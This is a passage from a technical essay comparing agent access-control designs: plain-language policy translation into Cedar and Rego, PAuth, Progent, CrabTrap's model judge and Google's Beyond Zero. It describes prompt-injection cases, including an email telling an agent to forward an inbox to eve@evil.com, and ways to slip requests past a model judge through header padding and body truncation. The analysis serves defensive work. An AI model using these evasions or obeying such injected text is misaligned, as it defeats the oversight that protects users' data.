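Silverlock's first reply is that a company needs one template for each type of task, however often it runs, so a nightly reconciliation needs only one. He also proposes a Grant Review Loop, which uses records from the broker, the harness and the network to suggest better templates. If a permission goes unused over many successful runs, the loop proposes removing it. If the broker keeps refusing the same operation and the work fails as a result, the loop can propose adding it, provided that the task description and the resource owner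 support the change. A person decides on each proposal, and any change applies only to later tasks, so an agent can't widen its permissions mid-task by repeatedly asking for more.

Silverlock acknowledges that the records can mislead. An attacker can repeat a forbidden request until it looks routine, and an unused permission may be there for a rare emergency. Suppose a nightly job needs a certain recovery step about once in 200 runs. The chance that the step goes unused in the first 50 runs is 0.995⁵⁰, or about 78%, so the loop would probably propose removing the permission for it. That chance falls to 5% only after about 600 runs, or 20 months. The records also show only what an agent used, so an agent that reads a whole customer database to find one address will appear to need the whole database.

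These errors are less serious than they sound. If a policy owner wrongly removes a permission, the next run that needs it fails visibly and the owner can restore it. A failed run is a much better way to discover a mistake in the permissions than a deletion. The loop seems likely to work well for jobs that repeat, and Silverlock sensibly recommends starting with one, such as a nightly reconciliation or an agent that sorts through logs.

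It offers much less for a request that nobody has made before, and much of the work people give to coding agents is like this. But a template can name resources instead of predicting steps, which may be enough for open-ended work. The agent at PocketOS was working in staging, and "any operation in staging, none in production" would have been easy to write as a template, even though nobody could have foreseen that the agent would try to delete a volume. The request contained only an identifier, so to enforce the template, the broker would have had to look up which environment the volume belonged to. Ordinary software can do that lookup, whereas the agent guessed.

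## The case for stating access policy in plain language

A template such as "any operation in staging, none in production" takes a few seconds to write in English. Software can enforce it only after someone translates it into code that names the operations and resources, and the people who know the rules often can't write that code. A support manager knows when an agent should give a refund, and a compliance officer knows which transfers need a second check, but few have learned a policy language such as Cedar. Supporters of plain-language policy would let these people state the rules in their own words and have a language model work out how they apply.

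Another argument for plain-language policy is that nobody can write rules by hand fast enough. Brex's *CrabTrap* reports that when the financial company put agents to work in its own business, each new agent capability required another hand-tuned token or another interface to audit. The available safeguards were either too strict for the agents to do their jobs or too specialized to use widely.

The proposals differ mainly in when the language model acts.

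| Design | When the model acts | What it reads | What decides on a request |
|---|---|---|---|
| Translating a standing policy | Once, when someone writes the policy | The policy and a list of tools | Fixed rules |
| Deriving permissions from a task | When the task begins, and in some systems as it proceeds | The user's task, and in some systems the results of tool calls | Fixed rules made for that task |
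| Judging each request | Whenever no fixed rule covers a request | The policy and the request | The model |

A model that acts later has more information about what the agent is trying to do, but its input is also more likely to include text written by an attacker, and people have less time to check its work.

### Translating a standing policy into rules

In *Authenticated Delegation and Authorized AI Agents*, South, Marro and colleagues (2025) favor using plain language to write a policy but not to enforce it. They think it is too risky to rely only on a model that interprets English permissions as it works, because the model may interpret a term like "sensitive data" differently in different contexts.

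In one example, a user tells the agent to read and write in the directories about a project called projectAlpha, but to stay out of the financial folders. A language model identifies these directories and writes a policy that lists them and denies access to one called financials2023. The user reviews the policy, corrects it if necessary and approves it. Ordinary software then enforces it without consulting the model.

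The model mainly helps by matching the user's words to real names, so the user doesn't have to remember what each folder is called. But the resulting rule names only the folders that existed when it was written. If someone later creates a folder called financials2024, the user's sentence covers it but the rule doesn't, and a policy that allows everything else in the project would let the agent in. South and colleagues acknowledge that instructions can fail to keep up with new resources in this way.

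The paper recommends limiting which resources an agent can use rather than which tasks it can do. A system can list its folders and databases, but a task like "draft a financial report" doesn't break down into a fixed set of operations. Resource limits also hold if someone tricks the agent. The same method could work between agents. If a project agent asks an accounting agent for some figures, the accounting agent replies with its interpretation of the permission, such as read-only access to two columns of one dataset, and the user or the project agent approves it. This is all a proposal, and the paper leaves testing the translations to future work.

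Amazon Web Services (AWS) sells AgentCore, a service for running agents. An agent's tool calls pass through a gateway, where a policy engine checks them against Cedar rules. According to AWS's *Policy in Amazon Bedrock AgentCore is now generally available* (2026), security and compliance teams can write these rules in natural language without changing the agent's code.

AWS's *Writing policies in natural language* gives the example of a sentence that allows a user named refund-agent to process refunds of less than $500. The service converts it to the following Cedar rule, shown here with shorter identifiers and without a routine check that the username exists:

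```
permit (
    principal is OAuthUser,
    action == Action::"RefundTool__process_refund",
    resource == Gateway::"refund-gateway"
)
when {
    principal.getTag("username") == "refund-agent" &&
    context.input.amount < 500
};
```

The phrase "process refunds" has become the name of one tool, and "the refund amount" has become the argument called `amount` in the agent's request. The rule also names a gateway, which the sentence didn't mention. The model can fill in these details because it has a description of the tools, and the service checks its output against the same description. AWS also analyzes the rule's logic with automated reasoning software, which can flag a policy that permits too much or too little, or one with a condition that can never be true. A company can first run a new policy in a mode that only logs its decisions, then let it block requests.

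Plain-language policies still have to be written carefully. AWS warns against vague conditions such as "when the amount is reasonable," and against writing "A or B and C" without making the grouping clear. The English needs most of the precision of code. Authors don't have to write the syntax, but they still have to decide exactly what the rule should be.

Marc Brooker, an engineer who works on agent policy at AWS, makes the argument behind the product in *Agent Safety is a Box*. He writes that people use agents because they are flexible and find their way around problems. A safeguard inside the agent has to restrict that flexibility, which makes the agent less useful. A "box" of fixed rules outside the agent can limit what it does without restricting how it plans. If the box allows only one refund per order, and never more than the purchase price, a company can work out the most it could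 lose on refunds without predicting the next prompt injection.

This argument doesn't require plain language. Brooker brings it in because "most people don't want to learn Cedar," and he is surely right about that. A box protects a company only if someone writes its rules, and more people can write them in English.

His refund example also shows a limitation of Cedar, which evaluates each request without considering earlier ones (InfoQ, 2026). It can limit the size of a refund but can't count refunds, so the rule above would allow a hundred refunds of $499. AWS has since introduced Dogwood, an open-source language that adds conditions about what has already happened in the agent's session. AWS's *Temporal policies* describes it as compatible with existing Cedar policies.

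AWS's *Authoring Dogwood policies from natural language in Amazon Bedrock AgentCore* shows the newer tool translating a whole document of rules for a bank's customer service agent. One rule allows refunds over $500 only if a supervisor approved them within the last 30 minutes. The translation denies any such refund unless the session's history shows that an approval request for the same charge was granted. Matching the charge number prevents the agent from using approval for one charge to refund another. Other rules require an identity check on the same account within 15 minutes before a transfer, and block transfers that would take the 12-hour total above $50,000.

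The tool first splits the document into individual rules and sets aside those that Dogwood can't express. A model translates the rest, and a compiler checks each result for valid syntax and real tool names. If the compiler finds an error, the model tries again, up to a fixed number of times. The user gets the finished policies, each next to its original sentence, and a list of the rules that the tool left out.

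That list may be as useful as the policies. In the bank example, it includes an instruction to act in the customer's best financial interest, which doesn't refer to any particular action, and a ban on weekend wire transfers, which Dogwood can't enforce because it can't look up the day of the week. A compliance officer who never saw the list might assume both rules were in force. Dogwood also can't apply a limit across sessions, so it could enforce Brooker's limit of one refund per order only within a single session. In a new session, the agent could refund the same order again unless the refund tool itself blocked it.

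When a model translates the policy in advance, it finishes before the agent starts, so nothing the agent reads can influence the rules. A person can also inspect the rules first, though they may not always notice a mistranslation, as discussed in the next section. But a standing policy has to be broad enough for every task it covers. A $500 limit suits a support agent that handles all kinds of refunds, but it is far too loose when the user has asked for a $90 refund.

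### Permission for one task and nothing else

*Beyond OAuth* (Sharma, Jiang and colleagues, 2026) proposes PAuth, a system that treats a user's request as permission for exactly the operations needed to carry it out. The paper distinguishes an operator, such as "transfer money," from an operation, which includes the details, such as "transfer $100 to Bob." An ordinary OAuth scope covers the operator, so a user who wants the agent to send Bob $100 also has to agree to transfers of other amounts to other people.

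Narrowing a credential's scope doesn't always work, because the right scope may depend on details that nobody knows in advance. Suppose a user with a Citi credit card and a Chase bank account writes, "If my Citi balance is over $1,000, pay a quarter of it from Chase." The right payment depends on a balance that the agent hasn't looked up yet, and Chase will make the payment but Citi holds the balance.

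PAuth begins by having the user sign the text of the task, so that the agent can't alter it. Both banks receive the text, and each works out for itself what requests to expect. At Chase, a language model translates the task into a short program in a restricted form of Python. Chase never runs this program. Ordinary software extracts from it only the parts that affect the payment, which Sharma and colleagues call a slice. In simplified form, Chase's slice looks like this:

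```
let balance = Citi.getBalance("my Citi account")
assert balance > 1000
Chase.transfer("my Chase account", "my Citi account", balance / 4)
```

The agent then asks Citi for the balance. Citi returns $1,200 in an envelope, a signed record that ties the value to the request that produced it. The agent attaches the envelope when it asks Chase to transfer $300, because Chase doesn't trust the agent to report the balance honestly. Chase checks Citi's signature, confirms that $1,200 is more than $1,000 and that a quarter of it is $300, and makes the payment. If an injected instruction had changed the amount to $301 or the recipient to a stranger, Chase would have asked the user whether to go ahead.

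The model that writes the program receives only the task and the tool descriptions. It never receives the web pages or emails that the agent reads, so an attacker can't use them to influence the program. If the model can't produce a valid program after several attempts, the service authorizes nothing automatically and refers the agent's requests to the user.

Sharma and colleagues tested PAuth on AuthBench, which they built by extending AgentDojo, a widely used set of simulated tasks for testing agent security. AuthBench has 100 tasks involving banking, shopping, travel, Slack messages and office work. The researchers also wrote 634 requests that a compromised agent might make, such as ones that change a recipient, use an unrelated tool or skip a condition. PAuth would have stopped to ask the user about all 634. It let the agent complete 71 of the 100 tasks in their original wording without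 asking. After the researchers rewrote the tasks to remove vague or indirect instructions, it let the agent complete all 100.

The 71 is the more informative result. A system that compares every detail with an expected value should catch a changed recipient, so the 634 requests mostly confirm that the software works. Real users are more likely to write like the original tasks. One of these asks the agent to update the rent payment without giving the new amount, which the rewritten version includes. The researchers suggest that the agent could look up such details first and ask the user to confirm a more exact version of the task. That would probably work, but it relies on the user to check what the agent has filled in.

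Sharma and colleagues also argue that a translation error is much more likely to cause an unnecessary question than a harmful payment, because a wrong rule would have to match the agent's wrong request by coincidence. This is persuasive for random errors but weaker when a task has two plausible readings, since the service's model and the agent's model may both choose the wrong one. In one of the paper's banking tasks, the user asks the agent to return $10 that a friend has just sent. The slice accepts a payment to the sender of the first matching $10 in the list of recent transactions. If two people had each sent $10, that sender might not be the friend. Sharma and colleagues treat ambiguity as a separate problem and assume that the user's task has only one meaning.

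PAuth is best suited to payments, bookings and other requests with exact details. When a model has to compose part of a request, such as a summary in an email, PAuth uses a placeholder that no value can match, so the service asks the user. Much of what a coding agent sends is text of this kind. Each service also has to see the full task, so a bank might see parts that the user would prefer to keep private. The cost is low, averaging $0.002 to $0.038 per task depending on the model, but each participating service has to pay it.

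The largest obstacle is that services have to adopt the system. Sharma and colleagues propose that a company could start with a trusted proxy that makes the same checks and holds the ordinary OAuth tokens. This proxy would be a broker that works out its own template for each task. Like other brokers, it could not stop the agent from using a stray token directly.

### A policy that changes as the agent works

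It is impossible to write an exact policy for some tasks at the start. *Progent* (Shi, He and colleagues, 2025) gives the example of a user who asks an agent to do whatever Alice's email "TODOs for the week" says. Until the agent opens the email, nobody can tell which tools the task needs. PAuth would ask the user about each request it couldn't predict. Progent starts with a narrow policy and changes it as the agent learns more.

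Progent sits between the agent and its tools. A language model reads the user's task and writes the first policy. In one example, that policy permits only a search for Alice's email. The email contains a request for a summary of recent messages, to be posted to the user's Slack account. The model then proposes permission to read emails, look up the user's Slack name and post a message. Once the agent finds that the name is `alice`, the model proposes allowing Slack messages only to `alice`.

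One of the recent emails contains an attack, an instruction to forward the whole inbox to `eve@evil.com`. The model that updates the policy has to read the same emails as the agent, so the attack may fool it too and lead it to propose adding permission to send email.

Progent deals with this by treating additions and restrictions differently. If A(P) is the set of tool calls that policy P allows, the system automatically accepts a new policy P′ only when

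A(P′) ⊆ A(P)

The new policy may allow only what the old one already allowed. Any other change is an expansion and needs approval, even if it adds one permission and removes ten. An SMT solver, a program that determines whether a set of logical conditions can all be true, compares the policies by looking for any tool call that the new one would allow and the old one would not. Restricting the Slack recipient passes this test, but adding permission to send email fails it, no matter how convincing the model found the attack.

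The system also has the model decide, before it sees the result of a tool call, whether that type of call could justify changing the policy. An email therefore can't lead the model to reopen the policy after, say, a call that only writes a file.

Shi and colleagues tested Progent by attacking live agents. On AgentDojo, 39.9% of attacks succeeded without Progent and 1.0% with it. On ASB, another benchmark of attacks on agents, the success rate was 70.3% without Progent and 3.9% with it. The agents still completed about as many legitimate tasks as before. In most of the remaining failures on ASB, the attacker's tool had a name and description very similar to those of a tool the task needed, and the researchers doubt that a person could have told them apart without knowing which tools to trust.

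For these main tests, the researchers had Progent approve every expansion automatically, to simulate a careless user. Because the system accepted expansions and restrictions alike, the solver's guarantee played no part in the results. The improvement came from the model's ability to write narrow policies and mostly ignore the attacks. On AgentDojo, even keeping the first policy unchanged reduced the attack success rate to 2.5%. These results are encouraging evidence that language models can write good policies, but they lack the certainty of a proof.

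The guarantee matters when a person or an automatic setting refuses expansions. Refusing every expansion was the most secure of the fully automatic settings on AgentDojo, but it would have prevented the agent from completing the task in Alice's email. When a person reviewed the first policy and each expansion, no attacks succeeded. Shi and colleagues expect this review to be manageable because only 6% of policy updates were expansions. However, they had already allowed common read-only tools for every AgentDojo task, so the agents rarely needed permission to look something up. A company that also restricted reading would probably see more requests for approval.

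The results for PAuth and Progent aren't directly comparable. Sharma and colleagues tested PAuth by sending prepared requests to a checker that demands an exact match, while Shi and colleagues tested Progent by measuring whether attackers could get a working agent to do something harmful. PAuth offers tighter control, even if malware takes over the agent's computer, because the services do the checking. Progent handles a wider range of tasks and needs no cooperation from the services. But when it runs as a separate proxy, it can't control tools built into the agent, so an agent with its own command line could bypass it.

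### A judge for unfamiliar requests

Brex's CrabTrap decides later still, after the agent has sent a request. It is an open-source proxy that decrypts an agent's web traffic in the same way as Agent Vault. It first checks each request against fixed rules, which match web addresses and, if the administrator wants, methods such as GET and POST. These checks take microseconds, and a rule that denies a request always overrides one that allows it. If no rule matches, CrabTrap sends the request to a model judge, a language model that evaluates it using a written policy for that agent. The judge returns a decision to allow or deny the request, with a reason.

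A model judge can read the body of a request to Railway's API and tell whether it adds a domain or deletes a volume, which a rule about addresses can't do. The judge would very likely have stopped the PocketOS deletion if the policy had let the agent manage only domains. But a policy of "any operation in staging, none in production" would have left the judge to guess which environment the volume belonged to, as the agent did.

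Brex's CrabTrap presents the request to the judge as structured data, with the address, headers and body in separate fields, so that text in the request can't be mistaken for part of the judge's instructions. It limits headers to 4 kilobytes, because an attacker could otherwise add enough junk to push the policy out of the model's context. It cuts off the body after 16 kilobytes and adds a warning for the judge that some of it is missing.

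Brex's claim that separating the fields prevents prompt injection is too strong, because the judge still reads the words, and a sentence such as "the finance team approved this transfer" may influence it wherever it appears. Hartman's broker ignores an agent's stated reasons because of this risk. A hijacked agent could also exploit the cutoff by filling the first 16 kilobytes with harmless text and putting the harmful part after it. A cautious policy would require the judge to deny any request it couldn't read in full.

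CrabTrap can also draft the policy. Many people find it hard to write one from scratch, and a rule that sounds sensible may block work that nobody thought of. The policy builder, itself an agent, drafts a policy that matches a sample of the monitored agent's past requests. The administrator then edits the draft and, before putting it into use, can replay old requests against it to see which decisions would change. CrabTrap can replay thousands of requests in minutes.

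Replaying requests is a very good feature that other policy systems should copy. It lets someone who can't read policy code see how a change would have affected last week's work. But old traffic contains only what the agent has already tried. If the agent has never tried to delete a database, the replay won't show whether the policy would stop it. And like Silverlock's Grant Review Loop, the policy builder may keep access that the agent used but didn't need.

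Brex reports that policies drafted from a few days of traffic matched human judgment on "the vast majority" of requests that the builder hadn't seen, but gives no figure. Even a high figure would be hard to interpret by itself, because if 99% of an agent's requests are harmless, a judge that allowed everything would agree with a careful person 99% of the time. Brex also doesn't report how many harmful requests the judge lets through, which is the important number.

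Brex says that in one deployment of CrabTrap, which it calls experimental, fewer than 3% of requests reached the judge. Agents soon settle into a routine, and administrators can turn the common requests into fixed rules. As Brex argues, this is a good answer to worries about delay. It is weaker evidence of safety, because the unfamiliar requests that reach the judge are also the most likely to be dangerous. As an illustration, suppose an agent makes 100,000 requests and the judge decides 3,000 of them. If it is wrong 1% of the time, it makes 30 wrong decisions, and a single deletion could matter more than the other 29 together.

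Brex also learned from the logs how many pointless requests its agents made, a benefit it hadn't planned. Its engineers used the logs to remove tools the agents didn't need, which reduced the agents' authority without relying on a model's judgment.

### Google's reasoning engine and Cloudflare's smaller grants

Google has a more ambitious plan to use AI in access decisions for both employees and agents. *Beyond Zero* (Valente and Zalewski, 2026) presents it as the successor to BeyondCorp, the model Google introduced in 2014, under which a company doesn't trust a request just because it comes from inside the company network. BeyondCorp mostly controls which applications a person may use, while Beyond Zero would decide whether a particular action on a particular file or record makes sense for the person or agent at that moment.

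Fixed rules set a minimum level of security. On top of them, a reasoning engine uses information about who is asking, what they are working on, how they normally behave and how sensitive the data is. It can allow the action, deny it or issue a challenge, which might require the person to explain the request, touch a security key or get a manager's approval. If the risk looks serious, the system can cut off some or all of the person's access while it investigates.

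In the paper's main example, an agent called SalesGenie with permission to read sales reports tries to open a confidential strategy document. BeyondCorp allows the request. Beyond Zero's engine finds that the user who prompted the agent works on financial services accounts in the Northeast, and that normally only the strategy and finance teams open this document. A policy requires a relevant work assignment for data this confidential, and the user doesn't have one. The system asks the user to confirm that the request was intentional, then to get approval from the team that owns the document. When the user fails to do so and a slower analysis finds other suspicious activity, the system restricts the user's access.

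A language model may have little role in the immediate access decision. Google's older systems already have trouble authorizing tens of millions of machine actions per second, and a model can't evaluate each one. Valente and Zalewski would therefore use AI mostly in advance, to classify documents and work out from personnel and project records what each employee is doing. The check at the moment of access can then be a quick comparison of stored facts, such as whether the user's assignment matches the document. Slower models look for patterns afterward, such as an employee opening far more files than colleagues do.

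A rule that employees may open only documents relevant to their work is easy to write, but a policy engine can't apply it without data on what each person is working on. Plain-language policies often lack such data, and AI could supply it by labeling people and documents in advance. Fixed rules could then enforce the policy, which is a sensible division of labor. The labels may be wrong, though, and a rule that relies on a mislabeled document will make the wrong decision every time.

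The system also has to monitor people closely. In another of the paper's examples, it raises an administrator's risk rating after detecting that they looked up basic questions an experienced employee should be able to answer. Someone might have stolen the account, but the administrator might equally be an honest person having a bad day. The penalty is mild, a request to touch a security key.

There is little public evidence yet of how well Beyond Zero works. *Going Beyond Zero* (Adkins and Ramamoorthy, 2026) says that early versions inside Google are detecting more misuse of access, but it gives no figures. It also says that Google kept the fixed rules because it is difficult to verify in advance what a fully dynamic system will do.

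Cloudflare's Agent Access Model also checks each action, but is meant to rely less on judgment. Silverlock warns that an attacker can influence a system's estimate of an agent's intentions through the same text that influences the agent. In his design, SalesGenie's task template would list only the sales reports, so the request for the strategy document would fail without anyone having to work out why the agent made it.

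Silverlock's approach is safer for a task that the company understands well. It is less convenient for a salesperson who has a good reason to see the strategy document, because the agent can't get wider access until someone authorizes a new task. Google's approach would let the document's owners approve the request on the spot. This flexibility is useful because people often can't predict what they will need. At companies that don't offer it, employees may give their agents broad permissions to avoid the trouble.

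Silverlock thinks the two approaches fit together, with fixed limits reducing what the reasoning engine has to decide. This works if the engine can't override the limits. If a model can only refuse a request or ask for more evidence, an attacker who fools it can still do only what the fixed rules allow. CrabTrap's judge has more power, because it can approve a request that matches no rule. CrabTrap administrators should therefore write fixed rules against the most damaging actions, since requests denied by those rules never reach the judge. Railway's API has a single address, so such a rule would have to block every request to it.

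## Whether a plain-language policy survives translation into rules

Suppose a manager writes, "The release agent may push fixes to our repositories but must not touch production." To push is to upload changes to a branch, one of the parallel versions of the code in a repository. The sentence seems clear, and a model could turn it into Cedar in seconds. One plausible translation has two rules:

```
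permit (
    principal == Agent::"release-agent",
    action == Action::"Push",
    resource in Company::"acme"
);

forbid (
    principal == Agent::"release-agent",
    action,
    resource in Environment::"production"
);
```

The agent may push to any branch in the company's repositories, but it may do nothing to the servers and databases in the production environment. Another plausible translation keeps those two rules and adds a third:

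```
forbid (
    principal == Agent::"release-agent",
    action == Action::"Push",
    resource
)
when { resource.deploysToProduction };
```

Suppose the agent tries to push a fix to the `main` branch of the website's repository, where an automated job publishes every change to the live site within minutes. The second translation denies the push, but the first allows it because a branch is not a server and the job that updates the site uses its own credentials.

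The sentence is ambiguous, since both translations fit it, and the translator has to pick one. The manager may only have meant to keep the agent off the production servers, in which case the second translation stops a release agent from releasing anything. Or the manager may have wanted a person to look at every change before customers get it, a step the first translation lets the agent skip.

In a translation error, the policy's meaning is settled but the rules don't match it. If the manager had explained that automatic deployment counts as touching production, and the model had still left out the third rule, that would be a translation error.

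The sentence also refers to fixes, which the rule language cannot express. Both translations omit this restriction because a policy engine cannot distinguish a fix from a new feature, so they let the agent push any kind of change. A better model will make fewer translation errors, but no model can determine from the sentence alone which meaning the manager intended, and no rule can test for a fix unless something else labels each change.

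### Rules that compile and rules that are right

Gupta and Sreenivasamurthy (2026), in *Prose2Policy (P2P)*, describe a tool they developed at Apple to translate plain-language access policies into rules. A language model first checks whether a statement is an access policy. It replaces pronouns with the nouns they stand for and splits compound statements, so a statement that nurses may read prescriptions but may not change them becomes two policies. From each policy it extracts the decision (allow or deny), subject, action, resource, condition and purpose. Ordinary software compares these with the organization's list of valid names. The model then writes a rule in Rego, the language of the widely used policy engine Open Policy Agent, and a style checker and a compiler check it for mistakes. Finally, the tool tests the rule on generated requests, some that it should allow and some that it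 should deny.

The researchers tried the tool on 485 statements from ACRE, a standard collection of access control requirements.

| Stage | Statements |
|---|---|
| In the test set | 485 |
| Accepted by the tool as policies | 389 |
| Produced a rule that compiled | 371 |
| Passed the tests for requests to deny | 367 |
| Passed the tests for requests to allow | 305 |

The paper's headline result is that 371 of 389 rules (95.3%) compiled, but compiling only shows that a rule is valid code. The tests of requests that should be denied add little, because a rule that denied everything would pass them all. On requests that should be allowed, 305 rules passed their tests, which is 63% of the original statements. Gupta and Sreenivasamurthy mostly blame the failures on poor tests rather than poor rules. They may be partly right, since the pass rate fell from 82.2% to 62.1% when the tests came from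 fixed templates instead of a model.

The bigger problem is that the tests and the rules come from the same extracted elements. If the model extracts "the assigned nurse" as "nurse," the rule lets in every nurse, and no test will involve a nurse who isn't assigned to the patient.

A follow-up paper, *Structured Decomposition for Reliable LLM-Generated Access Control Policies* (Gupta and Sreenivasamurthy, 2026), compared a revised pipeline with a single prompt that asked the same model, Claude, for Rego. A policy counted as correct only if it compiled and passed the style check and both kinds of test. The pipeline got 50.3% of 372 statements right, and the single prompt got 15.3%. Much of that gap arose because the single prompt rejected 295 statements, producing no rule for them, while the pipeline rejected 166. On the 77 statements that both attempted, the pipeline got 90.9% right and the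 single prompt 74.0%.

A rejected statement does little harm if the tool reports it, because someone can write the rule by hand. Wrong rules that compile are worse, and the paper describes four common types. The model may leave out a prohibition and rely on the engine to deny by default, so the action is allowed as soon as another rule permits it. It may drop a qualifier such as "for their team." It may apply a rule meant for one person to everyone in the same role. Or it may omit the default denial, so that some requests get no decision and the software that made them may treat this as permission. The single prompt got prohibitions right in three of eight cases, and the pipeline in seven. The samples are tiny, but the results are relevant to agent policies because rules such as "must not touch production" are also prohibitions.

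### Evidence from cloud policies and Cedar

In an earlier study, *Synthesizing Access Control Policies using Large Language Models*, Vatsa, Patel and Eiers (2025) took 47 AWS policies, most of them from user forums, and had a software engineer describe each one loosely in English. They then asked GPT-4 to recreate the policies from the descriptions. In most cases, the new policy allowed some requests that the original denied and denied some that the original allowed. When the engineer instead used a rigid notation, such as `ALLOW user:alice READ bucket:public-bucket/`, most of the results were more precise. The model was the same, so the loose descriptions probably caused much of the difference.

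GPT-4 also made mistakes when there was nothing to interpret. The researchers gave it 100 lists of individual requests, each marked allow or deny, and asked for a policy to match each list. Its policies were always valid code but handled only 83.82% of the requests correctly on average. That score overstates how well GPT-4 did, since most of the requests were marked allow and a policy that allowed everything might have scored about as well.

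Newer models do better, though unevenly. In *Neurosymbolic Characterization for Reliable Access Control Policy Analysis*, Vatsa, Hall and Eiers (2025) had models explain 587 AWS policies in English and then rebuild each policy from the explanation alone. Reasoning models, which work through a problem before answering, produced an equivalent policy in 36.0% to 93.7% of cases, depending on the model. Other models did so in 15.4% to 45.8%. The researchers say this design removes ambiguity because each model works from its own explanation. But an explanation can leave out details, so some failures may still come from the English.

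The most demanding recent test uses Cedar. Zhou, Vatsa and Eiers (2026), in *RAISE*, gave GPT-6 Astra and Claude Opus 5 one attempt at writing a policy for each of 375 sets of requirements. The policies were valid Cedar in 97.87% and 100% of cases, respectively. To count as correct, a policy also had to pass every logical check on what it must and must not allow. Only 33.60% and 30.67% did, although the average policy passed more than 70% of its checks.

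In one example, finance managers can make payments only in business hours, and the invoice needs approval unless the manager is on the corporate network. A model may write the network exception as a separate permission, which lets managers on that network pay at midnight. Zhou and colleagues count this as an error, but their policy sentence ends "unless the request comes from the corporate network," which a reader could apply to both restrictions. Some failures in the test may therefore be reasonable readings that differ from the one used in the checks. Zhou and colleagues generated the checks with a model-based system and reviewed only a sample of them. They acknowledge that the models they trained may have partly learned that system's way of interpreting ambiguous requirements.

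Translation seems to be much easier when the vocabulary is fixed. In a separate experiment, Zhou and colleagues trained a small open model on 1,024 policies for one invented organization, all using the same six actions. Its score on 256 new combinations of rules rose from 7.81% to 94.92%. Many companies have a fixed set of systems and use the same few kinds of rule, so this experiment may be closer to real use than a test that covers 44 fields. However, the organization was synthetic, and its policies contained nothing as vague as "touch production."

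### Perfect enforcement of the wrong rule

*Agent Security is a Systems Problem* (2026), a position paper by researchers at Google, NVIDIA and several universities, argues that a policy generated by an unchecked model call carries no guarantee of correctness, however strictly software enforces it. A policy engine guarantees only that it will apply the rules it has. If the manager wanted the third rule and the model left it out, the engine will allow every push to `main`.

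The paper also defines what a correct translation would be. Let A(N) be the set of requests that the natural-language policy allows and A(P) the set that the formal policy allows. The translation is correct if

A(P) = A(N)

in every situation the agent could encounter. Anything in A(P) but not in A(N) is access that the author ruled out. Anything in A(N) but not in A(P) is legitimate work that the agent can't do. The difficulty is that software can compute A(P) but not A(N). For the release-agent sentence there are at least two versions of A(N), one with the push to `main` and one without. A model could compare the sentence with the rules, but its verdict would only be probable. Words such as "sensitive" and "harmful" make matters worse, because their meaning depends on context that formal languages can't capture.

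The paper treats this as a research problem. It suggests defining key terms in advance (such as which websites count as trusted), restricting both the English and the rules until they can be compared reliably, and finding translation methods with a known limit on how far the rules can differ from the English.

Vatsa, Hall and Eiers describe the difficulty as a paradox. If the instructions are complete and unambiguous, existing tools can compile them without a model. If they are ambiguous, there is nothing to check the model's work against. The first claim is too strong, because complete instructions can still be in English, and most managers can't write a policy language such as Cedar. The second holds only if the person who wrote the instructions can't clarify them, and often the tool could ask.

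A fairer objection to the verification argument is that policies written by people don't come with a guarantee either. In *Reparo*, Mostofa, Zhang and colleagues (2026) ran policies that developers had published in 228 GitHub repositories through each language's official validator, and 55.7% of the Cedar policy statements failed. This probably overstates how bad the policies were. In one project that used another policy language, the only problem was a missing configuration file. Still, these figures make it hard to treat a handwritten policy as the safe default.

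A policy can also be useful without proof that it is correct. Progent's model-written policies had no such proof, and they stopped most attacks in tests. But that result is an average over many tasks, and a company with one production database cares most about the rule that protects it. The case for verification is strongest for actions that nobody can undo. There are usually few of these, so an engineer can write the rules that prohibit them by hand and leave the rest of the policy to the model.

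### Ways to check a translation

The main remedies catch different failures:

| Remedy | Ambiguity | Translation error | Inexpressible term |
|---|---|---|---|
| Generated test requests | Only if the author checks the expected answers | Often | Rarely |
| Automated analysis | Only by comparing two readings | Contradictions, and rules that allow everything or nothing | Names missing from the system's vocabulary |
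| Questions to the author | Yes, if the tool notices it | Sometimes | Yes, if the author can define the term or drop it |
| ActGov | No | Only those that break a stated requirement | Partly, if a model labels each case |

#### Generated tests

Tests are less likely to catch a mistake in a rule when they depend on that rule. In their follow-up, Gupta and Sreenivasamurthy made the tests less independent. If a test request that should be allowed lacks a field the rule requires, the software adds the field so that the request satisfies the rule. Suppose a rule wrongly requires a nurse to work in cardiology. A proper test would expose the mistake, but the software may put the nurse in cardiology and let the rule pass. Gupta and Sreenivasamurthy acknowledge that passing these tests does not show that a rule means the same as the original statement, and they plan to produce the rules and the tests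 separately.

In Reparo, one model writes a policy from an application's code, comments and documentation, and a model from a different company reads the same material and writes test requests with expected answers. Almost all of the policies were valid, but they gave the expected answer on only 82.0% to 86.5% of tests in Cedar and 76.3% to 80.2% in Rego. Two people reviewed 390 of the tests and judged 91.5% to 96.9% of them correct, depending on the language. Even the combined tests from two models left about a quarter of the Cedar rules untested. Mostofa and colleagues also warn that models reading the same evidence may make the same mistake.

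This is why generated tests don't catch ambiguity. If both models take "production" to mean only the servers, the test will confirm that a push to `main` should go through. The tests would be far more useful if the tool showed them to the policy's author. A manager who can't read Cedar can answer the question "Should the agent be able to push to `main`, which updates the live site?" CrabTrap's replay of old requests offers something similar, but a generated test can cover requests that no agent has made yet.

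A related method translates the rule back into English. *Extracting Next Generation Access Control Policies from Natural Language Using LLMs* (2026) describes a system in which a separate model call compares the result with the original sentence and sends doubtful rules to a person. This should catch a dropped condition, but it would probably accept either translation of the release-agent sentence, since both are faithful to it.

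#### Automated analysis

Logical analysis, which AWS uses to check its Cedar translations, can prove that a rule never applies or that two rules contradict each other. It can't show that a rule is too broad for its purpose unless someone has stated the purpose. Vatsa, Hall and Eiers give the example of a request to let developers read project files. A model might grant access to everything whose name starts with `project-`, even though the project files are all in `project-data/`. The rule is valid and consistent, and nothing in it suggests that it is too broad.

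Rules can also be too strict. *Autoformalization of Agent Instructions into Policy-as-Code* (Mondl, Maisel and Brock, 2026) describes converting an 88-rule policy for agents that handle medical records into Cedar. Ordinary software checked the syntax and logic, and a second model judged whether the meaning was right. Another team had previously coded 23 of the 88 rules by hand. When Mondl and colleagues replayed recordings of agents doing ordinary tasks, with no attacker involved, their policy blocked between 94% and 100% of the runs in which the agent tried to change a record. They present this as evidence that their translation covers more of the original policy than the handwritten version. It may, but a policy that blocked every change would have scored 100%, and they didn't measure whether agents could still do their jobs.

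Analysis is more helpful when it gives a person something to read. PolicySummarizer, built by Vatsa, Hall and Eiers, works out which requests a policy allows, has a model simplify the description, and rejects the simplified version if it differs too much from the exact one. In a user study, this raised people's accuracy on the hardest part of reviewing a policy change from 39% to 93%. Similar software can compare two translations and find a request that one allows and the other denies. For the release agent, it could find the push to `main`, which the tool should ask the manager about.

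#### Questions to the author

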